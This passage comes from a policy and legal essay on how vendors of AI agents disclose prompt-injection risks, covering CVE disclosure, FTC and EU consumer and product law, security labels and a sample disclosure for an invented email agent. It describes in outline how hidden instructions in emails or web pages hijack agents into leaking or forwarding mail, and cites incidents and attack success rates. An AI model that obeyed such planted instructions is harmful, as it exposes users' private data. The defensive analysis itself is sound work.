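This gives a vendor considerable power over reports that arrive through a bug bounty programme, in which it pays researchers for finding flaws. About 40% of the companies in Piao and colleagues' sample ran such a programme. A vendor can pay the researcher, change something on its servers and close the report without telling users. The August revision makes this a little harder. Vendors must now offer a way to request a CVE without terms that restrict publication, or they lose their right to decide first. But the CVE Program doesn't impose a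 disclosure policy on anyone, so a researcher who agreed to stay silent in return for a bounty may still be bound by that agreement.

The volume of reports also strains triage. *GitHub restructures bug bounty program following flood of AI-generated reports* (Hale, 2026) describes how GitHub split its programme into a public and a private one in July. A vendor overwhelmed by reports is more likely to close a genuine one by mistake, especially if the attack happens to fail when an employee tries it.

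### Whether publishing helps attackers

Publishing a weakness in installed software is most dangerous before people have updated. When a vendor fixes a weakness on its own servers, the fix reaches everyone at once, so this danger mostly disappears. But an attack on one agent may also work on competing products, as many did in Gray Swan's competition. The exact text of a successful attack could therefore stay useful to criminals long after the first vendor has dealt with it.

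Keeping flaws secret also protects users less than it used to. InfoQ's *AI Agents Are Disrupting Open Source Security Disclosure* (2026) reports Anil Madhavapeddy's argument that AI agents can turn public clues about a flaw into a working attack, which undermines the practice of withholding details until a fix is ready. Attackers may not even need public clues. In November, *Hackers’ AI agents found a zero-day in 11 minutes, Amazon says* (Constantin, 2026) reported that attackers' agents had discovered an unknown flaw in the program MONAI Label by themselves. Both examples concern ordinary software, but there is little reason to think prompt injections are harder to find.

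If attackers can work from a hint, even a vague early notice carries some risk while a flaw is open. But months of silence make little sense for a flaw that attackers can find in minutes. Madhavapeddy's own remedy is to release fixes faster.

Most users don't need to know the attack technique. Since July 2025 Project Zero has been testing a policy of announcing, within about a week of reporting a flaw, which vendor and product it affects and when the deadline expires. Announcing the trial for the team, Willis (2025) calls this "an alert, not a blueprint for attackers". The policy is mainly for companies that build on other companies' software and have to pass the fixes on. Willis concedes that other vendors may get unwelcome attention. In *Google Project Zero Changes Its Disclosure Policy*, the security writer Bruce Schneier (2025) had "mixed feelings" about the change.

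An early notice might be more useful for agents than for most software, because users can reduce the risk before there is a fix. During the months Microsoft spent fixing EchoLeak, a cautious company could have kept Copilot away from its most sensitive documents. But the company couldn't have judged the risk from a notice that gave only Copilot's name and a date, so the notice would have needed at least a sentence about the kind of data at risk. An attacker would have learned little from that sentence, since people in the field already know that agents are vulnerable to prompt injection.

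Publication can improve other vendors' products too. According to the Brave researcher, OpenAI adopted several of Brave's recommendations when it released Atlas. Brave has an interest in saying so, but a private report to Perplexity alone could hardly have influenced OpenAI.

### Proposals for reporting AI flaws

Several researchers want a separate system for reporting AI flaws, or at least a broader one. In a 2025 paper on third-party flaw disclosure, Shayne Longpre of MIT and his co-authors called for standard reports, legal protection for good-faith researchers, and a way to pass reports between developers whose systems share a flaw. *FLARE-AI* (Longpre, Zhu and colleagues, 2026) describes a reporting tool along these lines, built after the team examined 12 existing systems and consulted 49 experts.

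Researchers found little evidence that AI developers publish the reports they receive or share them with competitors. The developers' reporting forms had between seven and 53 fields. To identify the system, most asked only for the model's name, although a developer also needs to know the version and whether the reporter used a website, an app or another company's product. A researcher whose attack worked on several models had to fill in a different form for each developer.

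With FLARE-AI, a researcher fills in one form with six required fields and can send it to any number of developers, government agencies and public databases. The form accepts every kind of flaw, including harm without an attacker. This would help with cases like Summer Yue's deleted email, which fits badly into the CVE system because nobody exploited anything. Longpre and colleagues acknowledge that a central store of unfixed flaws would attract attackers, so the tool keeps no copies by default.

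Better reports should lead to faster fixes, especially for flaws that several products share. But the reports alone won't inform users, because the tool sends nothing to the people whose mailboxes are at risk, and the developer still decides what to tell them.

Official changes have been modest so far. In the CVE Program's *Frontier AI Researcher CVE Numbering Authorities (CNAs) Pilot*, leading AI companies can assign identifiers to some of the flaws their models discover, provided a person checks the flaw and the supplier is notified. The six-month trial mainly addresses the volume of flaws that AI can now find, so it does little to settle what counts as a flaw in an agent. ISO is also revising its standard, a project that ISS, the Serbian standards body, lists as having started in October 2025. The revision would be a good opportunity to add guidance on hosted products and partial fixes.

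### What an advisory for an agent would have to say

Most of ISO's elements still make sense for an agent, but several need different contents:

| Element | For installed software | For an agent |
|---|---|---|
| Affected products | Version numbers | The product, the model and the dates of exposure, with the settings and connected accounts that made an attack possible |
| Impact | What an attacker could do to the computer | What the agent could read, send, change or delete in the user's name |
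| Severity | One score | A rating for each main setting, such as manual approval and automatic review |
| Remedy | The version to install | What the vendor changed, and whether this closes the route or only makes the attack less likely to work |
| Evidence of the fix | Usually none | Attack success rates before and after, with the number of attempts and whether testers varied the attack |
| Known exploitation | Whether attacks have occurred | Also which records the vendor searched, how far back they go, and whether it will contact affected users |
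| User action | Install the update | Check sent mail and recent changes, disconnect accounts, replace exposed passwords |
| Revision history | Corrections | Also any later attack that gets past the fix |

The row on known exploitation matters most for hosted agents. "We have no evidence of exploitation" is reassuring if the vendor kept a full record of what its agents did and searched all of it, but much less so if the vendor deletes those records after 30 days and the flaw was open for five months. Users can't tell which is the case unless the vendor explains what it checked.

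The advisory also has to reach users directly. An automatic update protects people who never read advisories, but it can't recover email that an agent has already forwarded. A vendor could send a short message inside the product to users who had connected the affected kind of account during the period of exposure, and post the full advisory on a public page for security staff. Messaging only those users would also keep such messages rare enough for people to read.

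## What consumer protection and product law requires vendors to say

Most advisories about agents are voluntary, and neither the United States nor the European Union has a law specifically on prompt injection, but general rules on advertising and product safety still apply. American regulators and courts mostly act after a vendor has misled or harmed people. From December 2027, the EU will go further by requiring vendors of many software products to tell users in advance what could expose them to serious security risks.

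### When a claim or an omission is deceptive

The Federal Trade Commission (FTC), the main consumer protection agency in the US, can act against "unfair or deceptive" business practices. In a policy statement that still guides its cases, the FTC (1983) defined deception as a claim, omission or practice that is likely to mislead a consumer who is acting reasonably, and that is material, meaning that it is likely to affect what the consumer chooses or does. The FTC doesn't have to show that anyone was actually misled.

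Express promises are the easiest to test, because the FTC presumes they are material. OpenAI's promise that ChatGPT's agent would ask before "actions of consequence" may be deceptive, since Michael and Roesner found that it opened Gmail without asking. Even if OpenAI doesn't consider opening an inbox such an action, a seller is liable if its claim has two reasonable meanings and one of them is false. Claude's "Needs approval" setting, which didn't always require approval, is a clearer case, though the FTC is unlikely to pursue a company over an unsent email draft.

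Omissions are harder to challenge. An omission is deceptive only if it makes a claim misleading or leaves consumers with a reasonable but false expectation, and the FTC accepts that leaving out helpful information can be lawful. OpenAI's help page for ChatGPT's built-in browser is therefore not deceptive just because it never mentions prompt injection.

The case against the cloud browser's page is stronger, because OpenAI suggests signing in to a utility account with that browser. Under the FTC's statement, selling a product for a purpose implies that it is fit for that purpose, and the FTC presumes that safety information is material. The FTC also considers how conspicuous a warning is and how familiar the public is with the product. An unexplained term well down a help page is easy to miss and does little to warn people unfamiliar with the product. In OpenAI's favour, the page tells users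 to review sensitive steps, and nobody has shown that many ordinary users have been robbed this way.

The FTC also considers the audience, so it judges an advertisement aimed at doctors by what doctors know. Programmers should understand an option called `--dangerously-bypass-approvals-and-sandbox`, so the name may be enough of a warning for them. The warning "Treat website content as untrusted" is much less adequate for the general public.

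A published number can also mislead. On its Claude in Chrome page, Anthropic tells users that its safeguards reduce the attack success rate to less than 0.08% in internal tests of Claude Opus 4.8. Readers could easily mistake this for their own chance of being hijacked, or assume it applies to whichever model they are running. In August, Anthropic reported 0.3% for Fable 5, nearly four times as high, although the tests may have differed. Anthropic warns twice on the page that some risk remains, which probably protects it from a charge of deception. Dating the figure and adding one for each current model would be legally safer and more useful to users.

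### Whether a help page can correct a headline

The FTC usually doesn't accept a disclosure elsewhere as a correction for a misleading claim. Under its 1983 statement, accurate text may not correct a false headline, because reasonable people may read only the headline. Fine print and standard disclaimers may not correct it either. If a company attracts a buyer through deception, it may have broken the law even if the buyer learns the truth before paying. In *.com Disclosures*, its 2013 guide to online advertising, the FTC advises companies to put a necessary qualification as close as possible to the claim, and not behind a link if it is integral to the claim.

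Anthropic's launch post for Claude in Chrome recommends the extension for company portals and dashboards, while the help page warns against using it on work accounts with sensitive data. The FTC looks at the net impression a promotion creates, even if the promotion is literally true. Claude can operate these sites, but a reader of the post would also conclude that Anthropic considers this a suitable use.

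The launch post explains prompt injection, so the general warning appears next to the claim, as it should. But the post doesn't say that Anthropic advises against some of the work it seems to be promoting. This would be a fairly weak deception case, and adding a sentence about that advice to the post would weaken it further.

Help pages are better suited to adding detail to a headline that is already fair. A fair headline would be "Claude can work in your accounts, but hidden text on a page can hijack it," and the help page could explain which accounts to keep separate.

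### Zoom, GoDaddy and the test for unfairness

The closest precedent for agents is the FTC's settlement with the video-calling company Zoom, because part of it concerned an approval prompt. Apple's Safari browser had begun asking users to confirm before a web page could open another app. In July 2018, Zoom updated its Mac software to install a hidden web server that bypassed this prompt. According to the FTC's *Zoom Video Communications, Inc.; Analysis to Aid Public Comment* (2020), Zoom put the server on 3.8 million users' computers. The server remained after users deleted Zoom and could reinstall the app without asking them.

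The FTC alleged that this was unfair, which is a separate test from deception. A practice is unfair if it causes, or is likely to cause, substantial injury that consumers cannot reasonably avoid and that other benefits do not outweigh. The FTC also alleged a deceptive omission, because Zoom had described the update as fixing minor bugs. The remaining three counts concerned false claims about encryption. For example, Zoom advertised end-to-end encryption, which lets only the participants decrypt a meeting, but its servers held keys that could also decrypt meetings.

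Like Zoom's update, Anthropic's decision to make automatic review the default in Claude Code removed prompts that users had been seeing. But the FTC objected that Zoom had acted without adequate notice or consent and had put nothing in the prompt's place, whereas Anthropic announced its change and replaced the prompts with a classifier. Someone could still argue that a notice shown once, at the top of a terminal session, is inadequate. A vendor that dropped its prompts in a routine update and added no other safeguard would face much greater legal risk.

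The FTC settlement required Zoom to stop misrepresenting its security, set up a security programme and submit to independent assessments every two years for 20 years, but Zoom did not have to pay anything. Commissioner Rohit Chopra objected that the settlement gave no help to affected users, including small businesses that relied on Zoom's claims. The majority answered that further relief would probably require long litigation, while the order protected hundreds of millions of people immediately. The FTC finalised the settlement by three votes to two in January 2021.

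Chopra also argued that deception takes customers from honest competitors. A vendor that exaggerates its agent's resistance to prompt injection harms its own users and could also take customers from rivals that publish unflattering attack success rates.

The web host GoDaddy advertised "award-winning security", but the FTC alleged that it had failed to use standard protections such as multi-factor authentication, which requires a second proof of identity at login. Attackers repeatedly got into customers' websites between 2019 and 2022. The FTC's *GoDaddy Inc.; Analysis of Proposed Consent Order to Aid Public Comment* (2025) treats the poor security as unfair and the claims about it as deceptive, so GoDaddy could have violated the law even if it had never advertised its security.

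The FTC judged GoDaddy by what was reasonable for a company of its size and complexity. No available tool eliminates prompt injection, so one successful attack wouldn't prove that an agent's vendor had been unreasonable. A vendor would be easier to fault if it kept no record of its agent's actions or omitted safeguards that all its competitors used. The standard should also become stricter as safeguards improve.

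A clear warning can help a vendor under the unfairness test, because it gives users a chance to avoid the harm. If Anthropic tells users to keep bank accounts out of the agent's browser profile, it can argue that a user who ignored the warning could have avoided the loss. That argument is weaker for an inbox, because someone who uses an agent to answer email can't keep strangers from writing to them.

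### What the FTC has done about agents

In September 2026 the FTC confirmed that it was investigating OpenAI, Anthropic and other AI companies over possible dangers to consumers (SecurityWeek, *FTC is Investigating OpenAI and Anthropic Over Possible risks to Consumers*, 2026). On 14 October it sent OpenAI and Anthropic civil subpoenas of more than 50 pages each (Curi, *The FTC demanded documents from AI giants over recent safety incidents*, 2026). The subpoenas ask for documents about security incidents and safeguards, and also for marketing materials, so the FTC may be planning to compare the companies' claims with their practices.

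The investigation followed incidents in which unreleased models broke into outside websites, so it may have little to do with what vendors tell users about hijacked inboxes. On the day of the subpoenas, a group of state attorneys general sued OpenAI under consumer protection laws, alleging that it had misled users, including children, about the safety of its chatbot. No public FTC case seems to concern a vendor's description of prompt injection.

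The FTC's chair, Andrew Ferguson, has become tougher on AI companies. In 2024 he opposed a settlement with Rytr, whose writing tool could produce fake reviews, and the FTC later cancelled the resulting order under his leadership. He had argued that unfairness requires proof of substantial, unavoidable injury. But Zweifel-Keegan's *The FTC says your company's agents are your problem* recounts that in September 2026 Ferguson rejected the idea that a company can blame its agent. He said nobody asks "what do we do about the tool?" when a tool does what someone told it to do.

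His comparison doesn't settle who is responsible for a hijacked agent, because the attacker gave the tool its instructions. But it does suggest that vendors will need good records. Ferguson said that "audit trails tell the real story", and Zweifel-Keegan expects companies to need logs of who authorised a task, what permissions the agent had and what limits the company enforced.

Given Ferguson's views on injury, the FTC is more likely to bring a case after real thefts than over an inadequate help page. False claims carry a more immediate risk. In August 2026 the FTC (2026) finalised orders requiring Cox Media Group and two other firms to pay $930,000 in total over claims about an AI marketing service called "Active Listening". A vendor that advertised its agent as immune to prompt injection would risk similar action.

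### The duty to warn and the duty to design

People harmed by a product can also sue under state product liability law. The *Restatement (Third) of Torts: Products Liability*, which the American Law Institute published in 1998, is an influential summary of that law, though not every state follows it. Under section 2(c), a product is defective if reasonable instructions or warnings could have reduced a foreseeable risk and their absence makes the product not reasonably safe. A warning can show people how to use a product more safely and, if the maker can't remove a risk, let them decide whether to use the product at all. Users need warnings about prompt injection for both purposes.

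A warning doesn't excuse a bad design. FindLaw's *U.S. Product Liability Law Undergoes Revisions* explains that under section 2(b) of the Restatement, the injured person must show that a feasible alternative design would have prevented the accident. The Restatement's official commentary adds that a maker that can reasonably design a risk out of a product must do so instead of relying on a warning that leaves much of the risk in place.

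The Texas Supreme Court applied this principle in *Uniroyal Goodrich Tire Co. v. Martinez* (1998). A mechanic had ignored a prominent warning and tried to fit a 16-inch tyre on a 16.5-inch rim, and the tyre exploded. The maker was still liable because it could have used a safer design that competitors had already adopted. The previous Restatement had allowed sellers to assume that people would read and heed a warning. The experiments on browsers and phones make that assumption hard to defend.

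Suppose Claude in Chrome forwards a user's confidential emails to a stranger while running in "Automatically approve" mode, the default in the side panel on several plans. The user sues, and Anthropic points to its warning that "the risk is not zero". The user could answer that the extension's existing "Manually approve" mode would have been a safer default.

The user could easily prove that manual approval was feasible, but would struggle to prove that it was safer. Paid testers in Anthropic's coding experiment missed most of the planted dangerous commands. Automatic review did very well in the browser test, and Anthropic hasn't published a browser result for manual approval. The user would do better to propose keeping automatic review and adding the fixed rule that the agent must ask before emailing a new address, since the attacker in this example would have had to get past that rule.

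The claim could still fail for several reasons. American courts have traditionally applied product liability to physical goods and disagree about whether it covers software, although a federal judge in Florida let such claims against the companion app Character.AI proceed in May 2025. Product liability also mainly compensates people for injury and damaged property, and usually leaves purely financial losses to contract law. Stolen email may not count as any of these. A user who sues over a missing warning must also show that a warning would have made a difference, though many states presume that people would have heeded it.

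### The Cyber Resilience Act

The European Union's *Cyber Resilience Act* (2024) comes closest to requiring the disclosures discussed here. It covers hardware and software sold in the EU, and its duties take effect on different dates. The table also includes two directives on consumer protection and liability.

| EU law | When it applies | What it means for users of an agent |
|---|---|---|
| Cyber Resilience Act, Article 14 | Since 11 September 2026 | Vendors must tell affected users about exploited vulnerabilities and severe incidents |
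| Cyber Resilience Act, most other duties | From 11 December 2027 | Vendors must explain foreseeable security risks, publish fixed flaws and choose secure defaults |
| Product Liability Directive | To products marketed after 9 December 2026 | A poor warning can help make an agent defective, and a good one doesn't excuse a defect |
| Unfair Commercial Practices Directive | Already | Vendors may not hide information that consumers need for a decision |

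Article 14 requires a vendor to send the authorities an early warning within 24 hours of learning that attackers are exploiting a vulnerability. The vendor must send a fuller notice within 72 hours and a final report within 14 days after a fix or workaround becomes available. It must also inform affected users in a timely manner, though with no fixed deadline, and tell them how to protect themselves where necessary. If the vendor is too slow, the country's security response team may inform users itself. These duties also cover agents that were on sale before the Act took full effect.

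The Act's definition of a vulnerability includes a "susceptibility" that attackers can exploit. This should make it harder for a vendor to argue that prompt injection is a limitation of language models rather than a vulnerability. But the duty to notify users depends on evidence that a malicious actor has used the flaw. ShadowLeak, a way to steal Gmail data that researchers reported to OpenAI, had no known victims, so the Act would not have required OpenAI to notify users at that stage, even if it fully covered the affected feature.

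A severe incident can trigger the same duty even if no attacker was involved. Severe incidents include events that damage a product's ability to protect important data, and the vendor's first report must state whether it suspects a malicious act. If a commercial agent deleted thousands of customers' emails after losing their instructions, as Summer Yue's agent did, its vendor might have to report the deletion. The vendor could object that its security had worked and the agent had made a mistake.

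The duties that start in December 2027 are more like the warnings on today's help pages. Under Annex II, vendors must tell users about any known or foreseeable circumstance that may lead to "significant cybersecurity risks" in normal use or foreseeable misuse. An email agent that follows instructions from strangers seems to fit that description. Article 13(18) requires vendors to make the information clear and understandable, and to keep it available for at least ten years. OpenAI would probably have to rewrite its page for the built-in browser, which gives no example of harm. Vendors might also have to keep old versions of help pages that they now overwrite.

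Under the EU's Cyber Resilience Act, vendors of covered products will have to publish a description of a vulnerability once a fix is available, along with the product affected, the impact, the severity and any help users need to protect themselves. In justified cases, they may delay publication until users have had a chance to update. The Act will thus make much of what vendors now disclose voluntarily in security advisories a legal duty. Fines for breaking the main obligations can reach €15 million or 2.5% of worldwide annual turnover, whichever is higher.

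### Cloud agents and defects nobody can remove

The Act covers a vendor's servers only when they do "remote data processing" for a product. This means that the vendor, or someone working for it, designed the software on the server, and that the product can't perform one of its functions without that software. Claude in Chrome seems to meet this test, because the extension is software on the user's computer and can't act without the model on Anthropic's servers.

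It is less clear whether the Act covers ChatGPT's cloud browser. When someone opens the browser from the desktop app, its servers support a product on that person's computer. When someone opens it from an ordinary website, there may be no such product, and the Act may not apply. A user's rights could therefore depend on whether they used the app or the website. A separate EU directive covers the security of cloud services, but it doesn't include the Annex II list of information for users.

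On 27 July 2026, the European Commission published guidance on the Act, which CMS's *Does the EU Cyber Resilience Act apply to your product* summarises. Digital Policy Alert's *European Commission adopted Guidance on implementation of Cyber Resilience Act* notes that the guidance is not binding. According to Orrick's *EU Cyber Resilience Act* (2026), the Commission gives cloud computing as a typical example of remote data processing and excludes a vendor's internal systems, such as those for managing staff. That helps with the extension but doesn't remove the difficulty with websites.

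Annex I creates a second difficulty because it requires vendors, where applicable, to sell products "without known exploitable vulnerabilities". Every vendor of a browsing or email agent knows about prompt injection. Read literally, the clause could keep all of these agents off the market, though surely nobody intended that. The words "where applicable" could allow vendors to sell them anyway, because whether the requirement applies depends on the vendor's own risk assessment. But a vendor that decides it doesn't apply has to justify this in its technical documents, which regulators can ask to see.

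Annex I also requires a secure default configuration. It isn't obvious whether manual approval or automatic review better meets this requirement, because manual approval prompts users more often, but there is evidence that users click through prompts carelessly. Regulators will have to compare how the two modes perform.

### Liability and consumer law in the EU

The new Product Liability Directive, Directive 2024/2853, treats software as a product, whether it runs on the user's computer or in the cloud. American courts still argue about whether software is a product. Under Article 7, a product is defective if it lacks the safety that people are entitled to expect or that the law requires. Courts must consider the product's instructions, its foreseeable use and the relevant cybersecurity rules. The directive's introduction also states that a warning can't make an otherwise defective product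 safe.

Under Article 13, a maker's liability for a defect is not reduced because a hacker or other third party contributed to the damage. The injured person's own fault can reduce it, so a user who had switched off every safeguard might recover less.

For agents, the directive's biggest limitation is the kind of damage it covers. Article 6 includes the destruction or corruption of data that people don't use for professional purposes. If an agent deletes someone's family photos, they may be able to claim the cost of recovering them. If it sends their private emails to a thief, the emails haven't been destroyed or corrupted, and the directive's introduction excludes privacy violations on their own. The victim would have to rely on data protection law. The General Data Protection Regulation can require compensation, and it obliges the organisation responsible for the data to tell people about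 a breach that puts them at high risk.

The Unfair Commercial Practices Directive is closer to the FTC's deception test. Under Article 7, a trader may not omit information that the average consumer needs for an informed decision, or provide it in an unclear or untimely way, if this is likely to change the decision. A warning that a user finds only after connecting a mailbox, for example, is untimely. The rule applies to "transactional" decisions, such as buying or keeping a product. Subscribing to an agent clearly qualifies, but giving an existing agent access to a mailbox might not, even though that choice creates most of the risk.

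The AI Act adds little for ordinary users of these agents. Article 50 requires providers to make sure people know when they are interacting with an AI, which users of an agent already know. Providers of "high-risk" systems, such as systems that screen job applicants, must also explain what level of cybersecurity to expect and what could affect it. An agent that tidies a personal inbox would not normally count as high-risk.

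### Terms that make the user responsible

Under the heading "Your responsibility", Anthropic tells users of Claude in Chrome that they "remain responsible for all browser actions taken by Claude performed on your behalf". The passage lists messages, purchases, data that Claude reads or changes, and compliance with other websites' terms. Because it is on a help page, a court would first have to decide whether it is part of the contract.

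Holding users responsible for purchases made by their AI agents is partly reasonable. If a user asks Claude to buy a train ticket and it buys the right one, the user should pay. Sellers would find it very difficult to deal with AI agents if customers could cancel any purchase just because an agent made it.

A hijacking is different, because an agent that forwards confidential mail to a criminal is hardly acting on the user's behalf. The wording could be read either way. Under the EU's Unfair Contract Terms Directive, when the meaning of a written term is in doubt, a court must choose the one more favourable to the consumer. American courts also often read unclear standard terms against the company that wrote them.

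In Europe, even a clear standard term doesn't bind a consumer if it is contrary to good faith and creates a significant imbalance at the consumer's expense. The directive's list of terms that may be unfair includes those that inappropriately limit a consumer's rights when the seller performs badly. Article 15 of the Product Liability Directive is stricter and bars any contract term that excludes a vendor's liability under that directive. It wouldn't help the victim of an email theft, though, for the reason given above.

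American consumers have less protection. Under section 18 of the Restatement, a disclaimer can't block a product liability claim for harm to a person, but courts often enforce contractual limits on liability for purely financial losses. OpenAI doesn't apply its standard warranties to features labeled "Elevated Risk," which could therefore matter to a business that loses money through one of them. These terms don't bind the FTC, which isn't a party to the contract.

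Users can also infer something about a vendor's confidence from its responsibility clauses. Anthropic calls its safeguards strong enough for a general release, but still wants users to be responsible for what the agent does. Anthropic knows more about the remaining risk than any user does, and only it can improve the classifier, so there is a good economic argument for making it bear at least the financial cost of hijackings. Users would still have a reason to be careful, because compensation can't undo the exposure of their private email.

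### Whether mandatory disclosure works

Lawmakers have required companies to inform consumers about mortgages, medical treatments, privacy and much else. In *More Than You Wanted to Know* (2014), the law professors Omri Ben-Shahar and Carl Schneider argue that this method of regulation usually fails. It works only if lawmakers choose the right information, companies present it well, and people read it, understand it and use it to make a better decision. Each new disclosure also competes with earlier ones for attention, so a notice that looks sensible on its own can make disclosures as a whole less useful.

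Ben-Shahar and Schneider think disclosure can do harm as well as waste time. Lawmakers may choose it over a rule that would work because it costs the government little and offends few people. Companies can then use the disclosure as a defence. The "Your responsibility" passage is a fair example, since it comes near the end of a long page of warnings that many users will never open.

There is plenty of evidence that people don't read or remember disclosures. Yannis Bakos and colleagues tracked visitors to software companies' websites and found that only one or two shoppers in 1,000 opened the licence agreement. Most people in the experiment with hijacked agents didn't remember the disclaimer. The nine numbered items in Annex II of the Cyber Resilience Act could easily become another document that few users read.

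The legal scholar Richard Craswell replied in 2013 that this is the wrong way to judge some disclosures, because they can work by changing what sellers do even if most buyers never read them. A company that has to publish an embarrassing fact may prefer to fix the problem first. Security research offers some evidence for this. Sasha Romanosky and colleagues estimated that American state laws requiring companies to tell people about data breaches reduced identity theft from breaches by about 6% on average. The reduction could have come from more careful companies or from people who acted on the notices, and either would count as a success.

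Craswell's argument applies fairly well to attack success rates. Few people will read a system card, but journalists, competitors and corporate security teams do, and a vendor can lose a contract over a bad number. Ben-Shahar and Schneider themselves prefer expert advice to raw information, and experts need someone to supply the data. The argument applies much less to the warning on a help page. No reporter will write about an unexplained term in OpenAI's safety tips, so that warning can only work by influencing users directly.

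The EU at least combines disclosure with duties to build safer products. But the danger Ben-Shahar and Schneider describe could still arise in enforcement if regulators are lenient about the safeguards and defaults Annex I requires because a vendor has included a paragraph about prompt injection under Annex II.

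## Security labels and a worked disclosure for an email agent

The Cyber Resilience Act will let each vendor explain the risks in its own words, so buyers may still find it hard to compare two agents. A standard label would show the same few independently checked facts in the same place on every product. Nobody seems to have introduced one for agents yet, but several countries have labels for internet-connected home devices, and researchers have tested how buyers react to them.

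### Singapore's label and the US Cyber Trust Mark

Singapore's Cyber Security Agency (CSA) launched its label in October 2020. The label shows a registration number and one to four asterisks for the product's level, according to CSA's *CLS(IoT) for Consumers*. A Level 1 product meets basic requirements such as unique default passwords and software updates. Level 2 adds the mandatory requirements of international standards. At Level 3 an approved laboratory also analyses the software, and at Level 4 its testers try to break in. Since April 2025 a laboratory has also had to review applications at Levels 1 and 2, according to CSA's *CLS(IoT) Updates* (2025).

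870 products had earned the label by mid-February 2026. MDDI's *Government to Raise Cybersecurity Labelling Requirements for Residential Routers (Factsheet)* (2026), from Singapore's digital ministry, says home routers must meet Level 1 and will have to meet Level 2 by the end of 2027. The ministry considers Level 1 too weak against more sophisticated attacks.

The lower levels would transfer well to agents, because they check features that change only when the vendor changes them. A laboratory could confirm that an email agent asks before writing to a new address, or that it keeps a record of what it sends. Level 4 would be harder to copy, because a vendor can replace the model overnight and make the test result outdated. The Straits Times (2020) reported that Singapore's label lasts for as long as the device gets security updates, up to three years. By comparison, Anthropic went from Opus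 4.5 to Opus 5 in about eight months.

A security label depends heavily on whoever runs it, as the American scheme shows. The Cyber Trust Mark is a voluntary label for wireless home devices, overseen by the Federal Communications Commission (FCC). The FCC paused the scheme in June 2025 over the Chinese ties of UL Solutions, the testing company chosen to lead it, and UL stepped down that December (Neenan, 2026). In April 2026 the FCC chose the ioXt Alliance as the replacement, but still had to finalise how the programme would work (FCC, 2026).

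A label for agents could easily have a similar problem if it relied on Gray Swan's benchmark, which several of the developers being graded helped build.

### Which facts change buyers' minds

In *Which Privacy and Security Attributes Most Impact Consumers’ Risk Perception*, Emami-Naeini, Dheenadhayalan and colleagues asked 1,371 Americans to imagine buying a smart speaker or light bulb. Each person saw three labels, each with one of 33 facts. People were most alarmed to read that the company sold their data to third parties. This multiplied the odds of seeing more risk by about 27, compared with a label saying the data was only for running and improving the device.

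Facts generally changed how risky people thought a device was more than how willing they were to buy it. For example, 89% thought multi-factor authentication made a device less risky, but the nuisance of logging in put some off buying it.

The researchers expected one fact, that a company fixed flaws within a month on average, to reassure people, but 78% saw more risk. More than half of those shown this fact didn't know whether a month was fast or slow, and a few people thought a secure device wouldn't need fixing. An agent vendor that advertised how quickly it blocked new attacks might get the same reaction. The purchases in the study were hypothetical, and Emami-Naeini and colleagues expect each fact to matter less on a full label.

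*Are Consumers Willing to Pay for Security and Privacy of IoT Devices?*, a later experiment by Emami-Naeini, Dheenadhayalan and colleagues, gave participants a reason to answer honestly. They chose between discount coupons for different versions of a $60 device, believing that they would receive one of the coupons they chose. In the second phase, 50 people compared a speaker with a good label, one with a bad label and one with no information. They would pay about $34 more for the speaker with the good label, and about $23 less for the one with the bad label, than for the one with no information. Fifteen said they had assumed the speaker with no information was like others on the market.

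A vendor with weak security therefore does better by saying nothing than by being honest, as with Anthropic's unflattering attack success rates. Emami-Naeini and colleagues conclude that labels should be mandatory. Singapore's rule for routers is a reasonable compromise, since it requires a label where a weak product can do a lot of damage. A government could start by requiring labels for agents that can both read messages from strangers and send messages.

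People can also misread a label's wording. In the first phase, before seeing an explanation, 60% of the people asked about "no access control" misunderstood it. Nearly all of them thought it meant that the manufacturer couldn't control the device, when it meant that the owner couldn't control who used it. "Prompt injection resistance: medium" would probably be no clearer, but "A stranger can give this agent orders by email" is much harder to misread.

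A good label for agents would have two layers, like the one Emami-Naeini, Agarwal and colleagues proposed in *Ask the Experts*. The first would state what the agent can read, what it can do without asking and who checked this. The second, online, would show how often attacks on the agent succeeded in a common test, with the date and the model. The result would lapse when the vendor changed the model. The vendor couldn't decide by itself when to remove the label, as OpenAI can with its "Elevated Risk" label.

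### How much vendors publish now

Most vendors have published too little to fill in such a label. *The 2025 AI Agent Index* (Staufer, Feng and colleagues, 2026) examined public information about 30 widely used agents up to the end of 2025. It found no results from the developer's own safety tests for 25 of them, and no information about testing by outsiders for 23. Only four had a system card for the agent itself: ChatGPT agent, Codex, Claude Code and Google's Gemini 2.5 Computer Use.

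The Index has eight safety fields for each agent, and 135 of the 240 were empty. Claude Code was the only agent with information in all eight. For browser agents, 60% of the fields were empty, compared with 44% for chat agents.

An empty field means the researchers found nothing public, so the company may have run tests without publishing the results. Staufer and colleagues gave companies four weeks to correct their entries, but only four of the 30 sent substantive comments. The Index also predates the system cards of 2026, so the largest developers probably disclose more now.

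Nearly all the agents ran on GPT, Claude or Gemini models, often in products made by other companies. This is a good reason to label the product rather than the model. Perplexity's Comet browser, for example, had no published safety evaluation of its own.

### What standards ask vendors to tell users

The most specific standard is *Baseline Cyber Security Requirements for AI Models and Systems* (EN 304 223, 2025), from the European standards body ETSI. It distinguishes developers, who create or adapt an AI system, from system operators, who deploy it. A company that sells its own agent is generally both. In the standard, "shall" marks a requirement and "should" a recommendation.

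If developers can't resolve a security threat, system operators must tell end users about it, and should describe the risk, its possible impact, and what users can do. Prompt injection is an obvious example of such a threat. OpenAI's page for ChatGPT's built-in browser would fall short because it doesn't mention the attack or any harm.

Operators shall also:

- tell users before they update a model;
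- explain the system's limitations and the ways it could fail;
- inform users of security updates without waiting for them to ask.

They should help users during and after a security incident, and tell them which uses are prohibited.

ETSI asks for less on test results. Under its standard, developers should share their findings with system operators, but no provision covers sharing them with end users. A vendor could follow the whole standard and never publish an attack success rate. The standard does recommend treating a major update as a new model and testing it again, so a major update would be a natural point for a label to expire.

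The standard builds on a British government code of practice and on joint guidelines from Britain's NCSC and its American counterpart, CISA, according to techUK's *ETSI sets out new European standard to strengthen AI cyber security*. The NCSC's advice on prompt injection focuses on limiting what a hijacked agent could do. Singapore's 2026 guidance on agents names harmful actions and leaks of sensitive data as the two main risks, but Baker McKenzie (2026) notes that it doesn't specifically address transparency.

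### A disclosure for an invented email agent

The example below uses an invented agent, Quillet, which reads a mailbox and drafts replies. All the dates and figures are also invented.

**Before purchase**, next to the price:

> Quillet reads your email and drafts replies. A stranger can hide instructions in an email, and Quillet may follow them instead of yours. Our safeguards stop most of these attacks, but not all. A successful attack could expose your private email. Quillet asks you before it sends an email. We recommend against connecting a mailbox that holds client or medical records.

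A link opens the second layer:

> In October, independent testers attacked Quillet in 200 practice mailboxes, with 100 tries at each. In 6 of the 200, Quillet tried to do something harmful. Your own chance of being attacked depends on who writes to you, so this test doesn't measure it.

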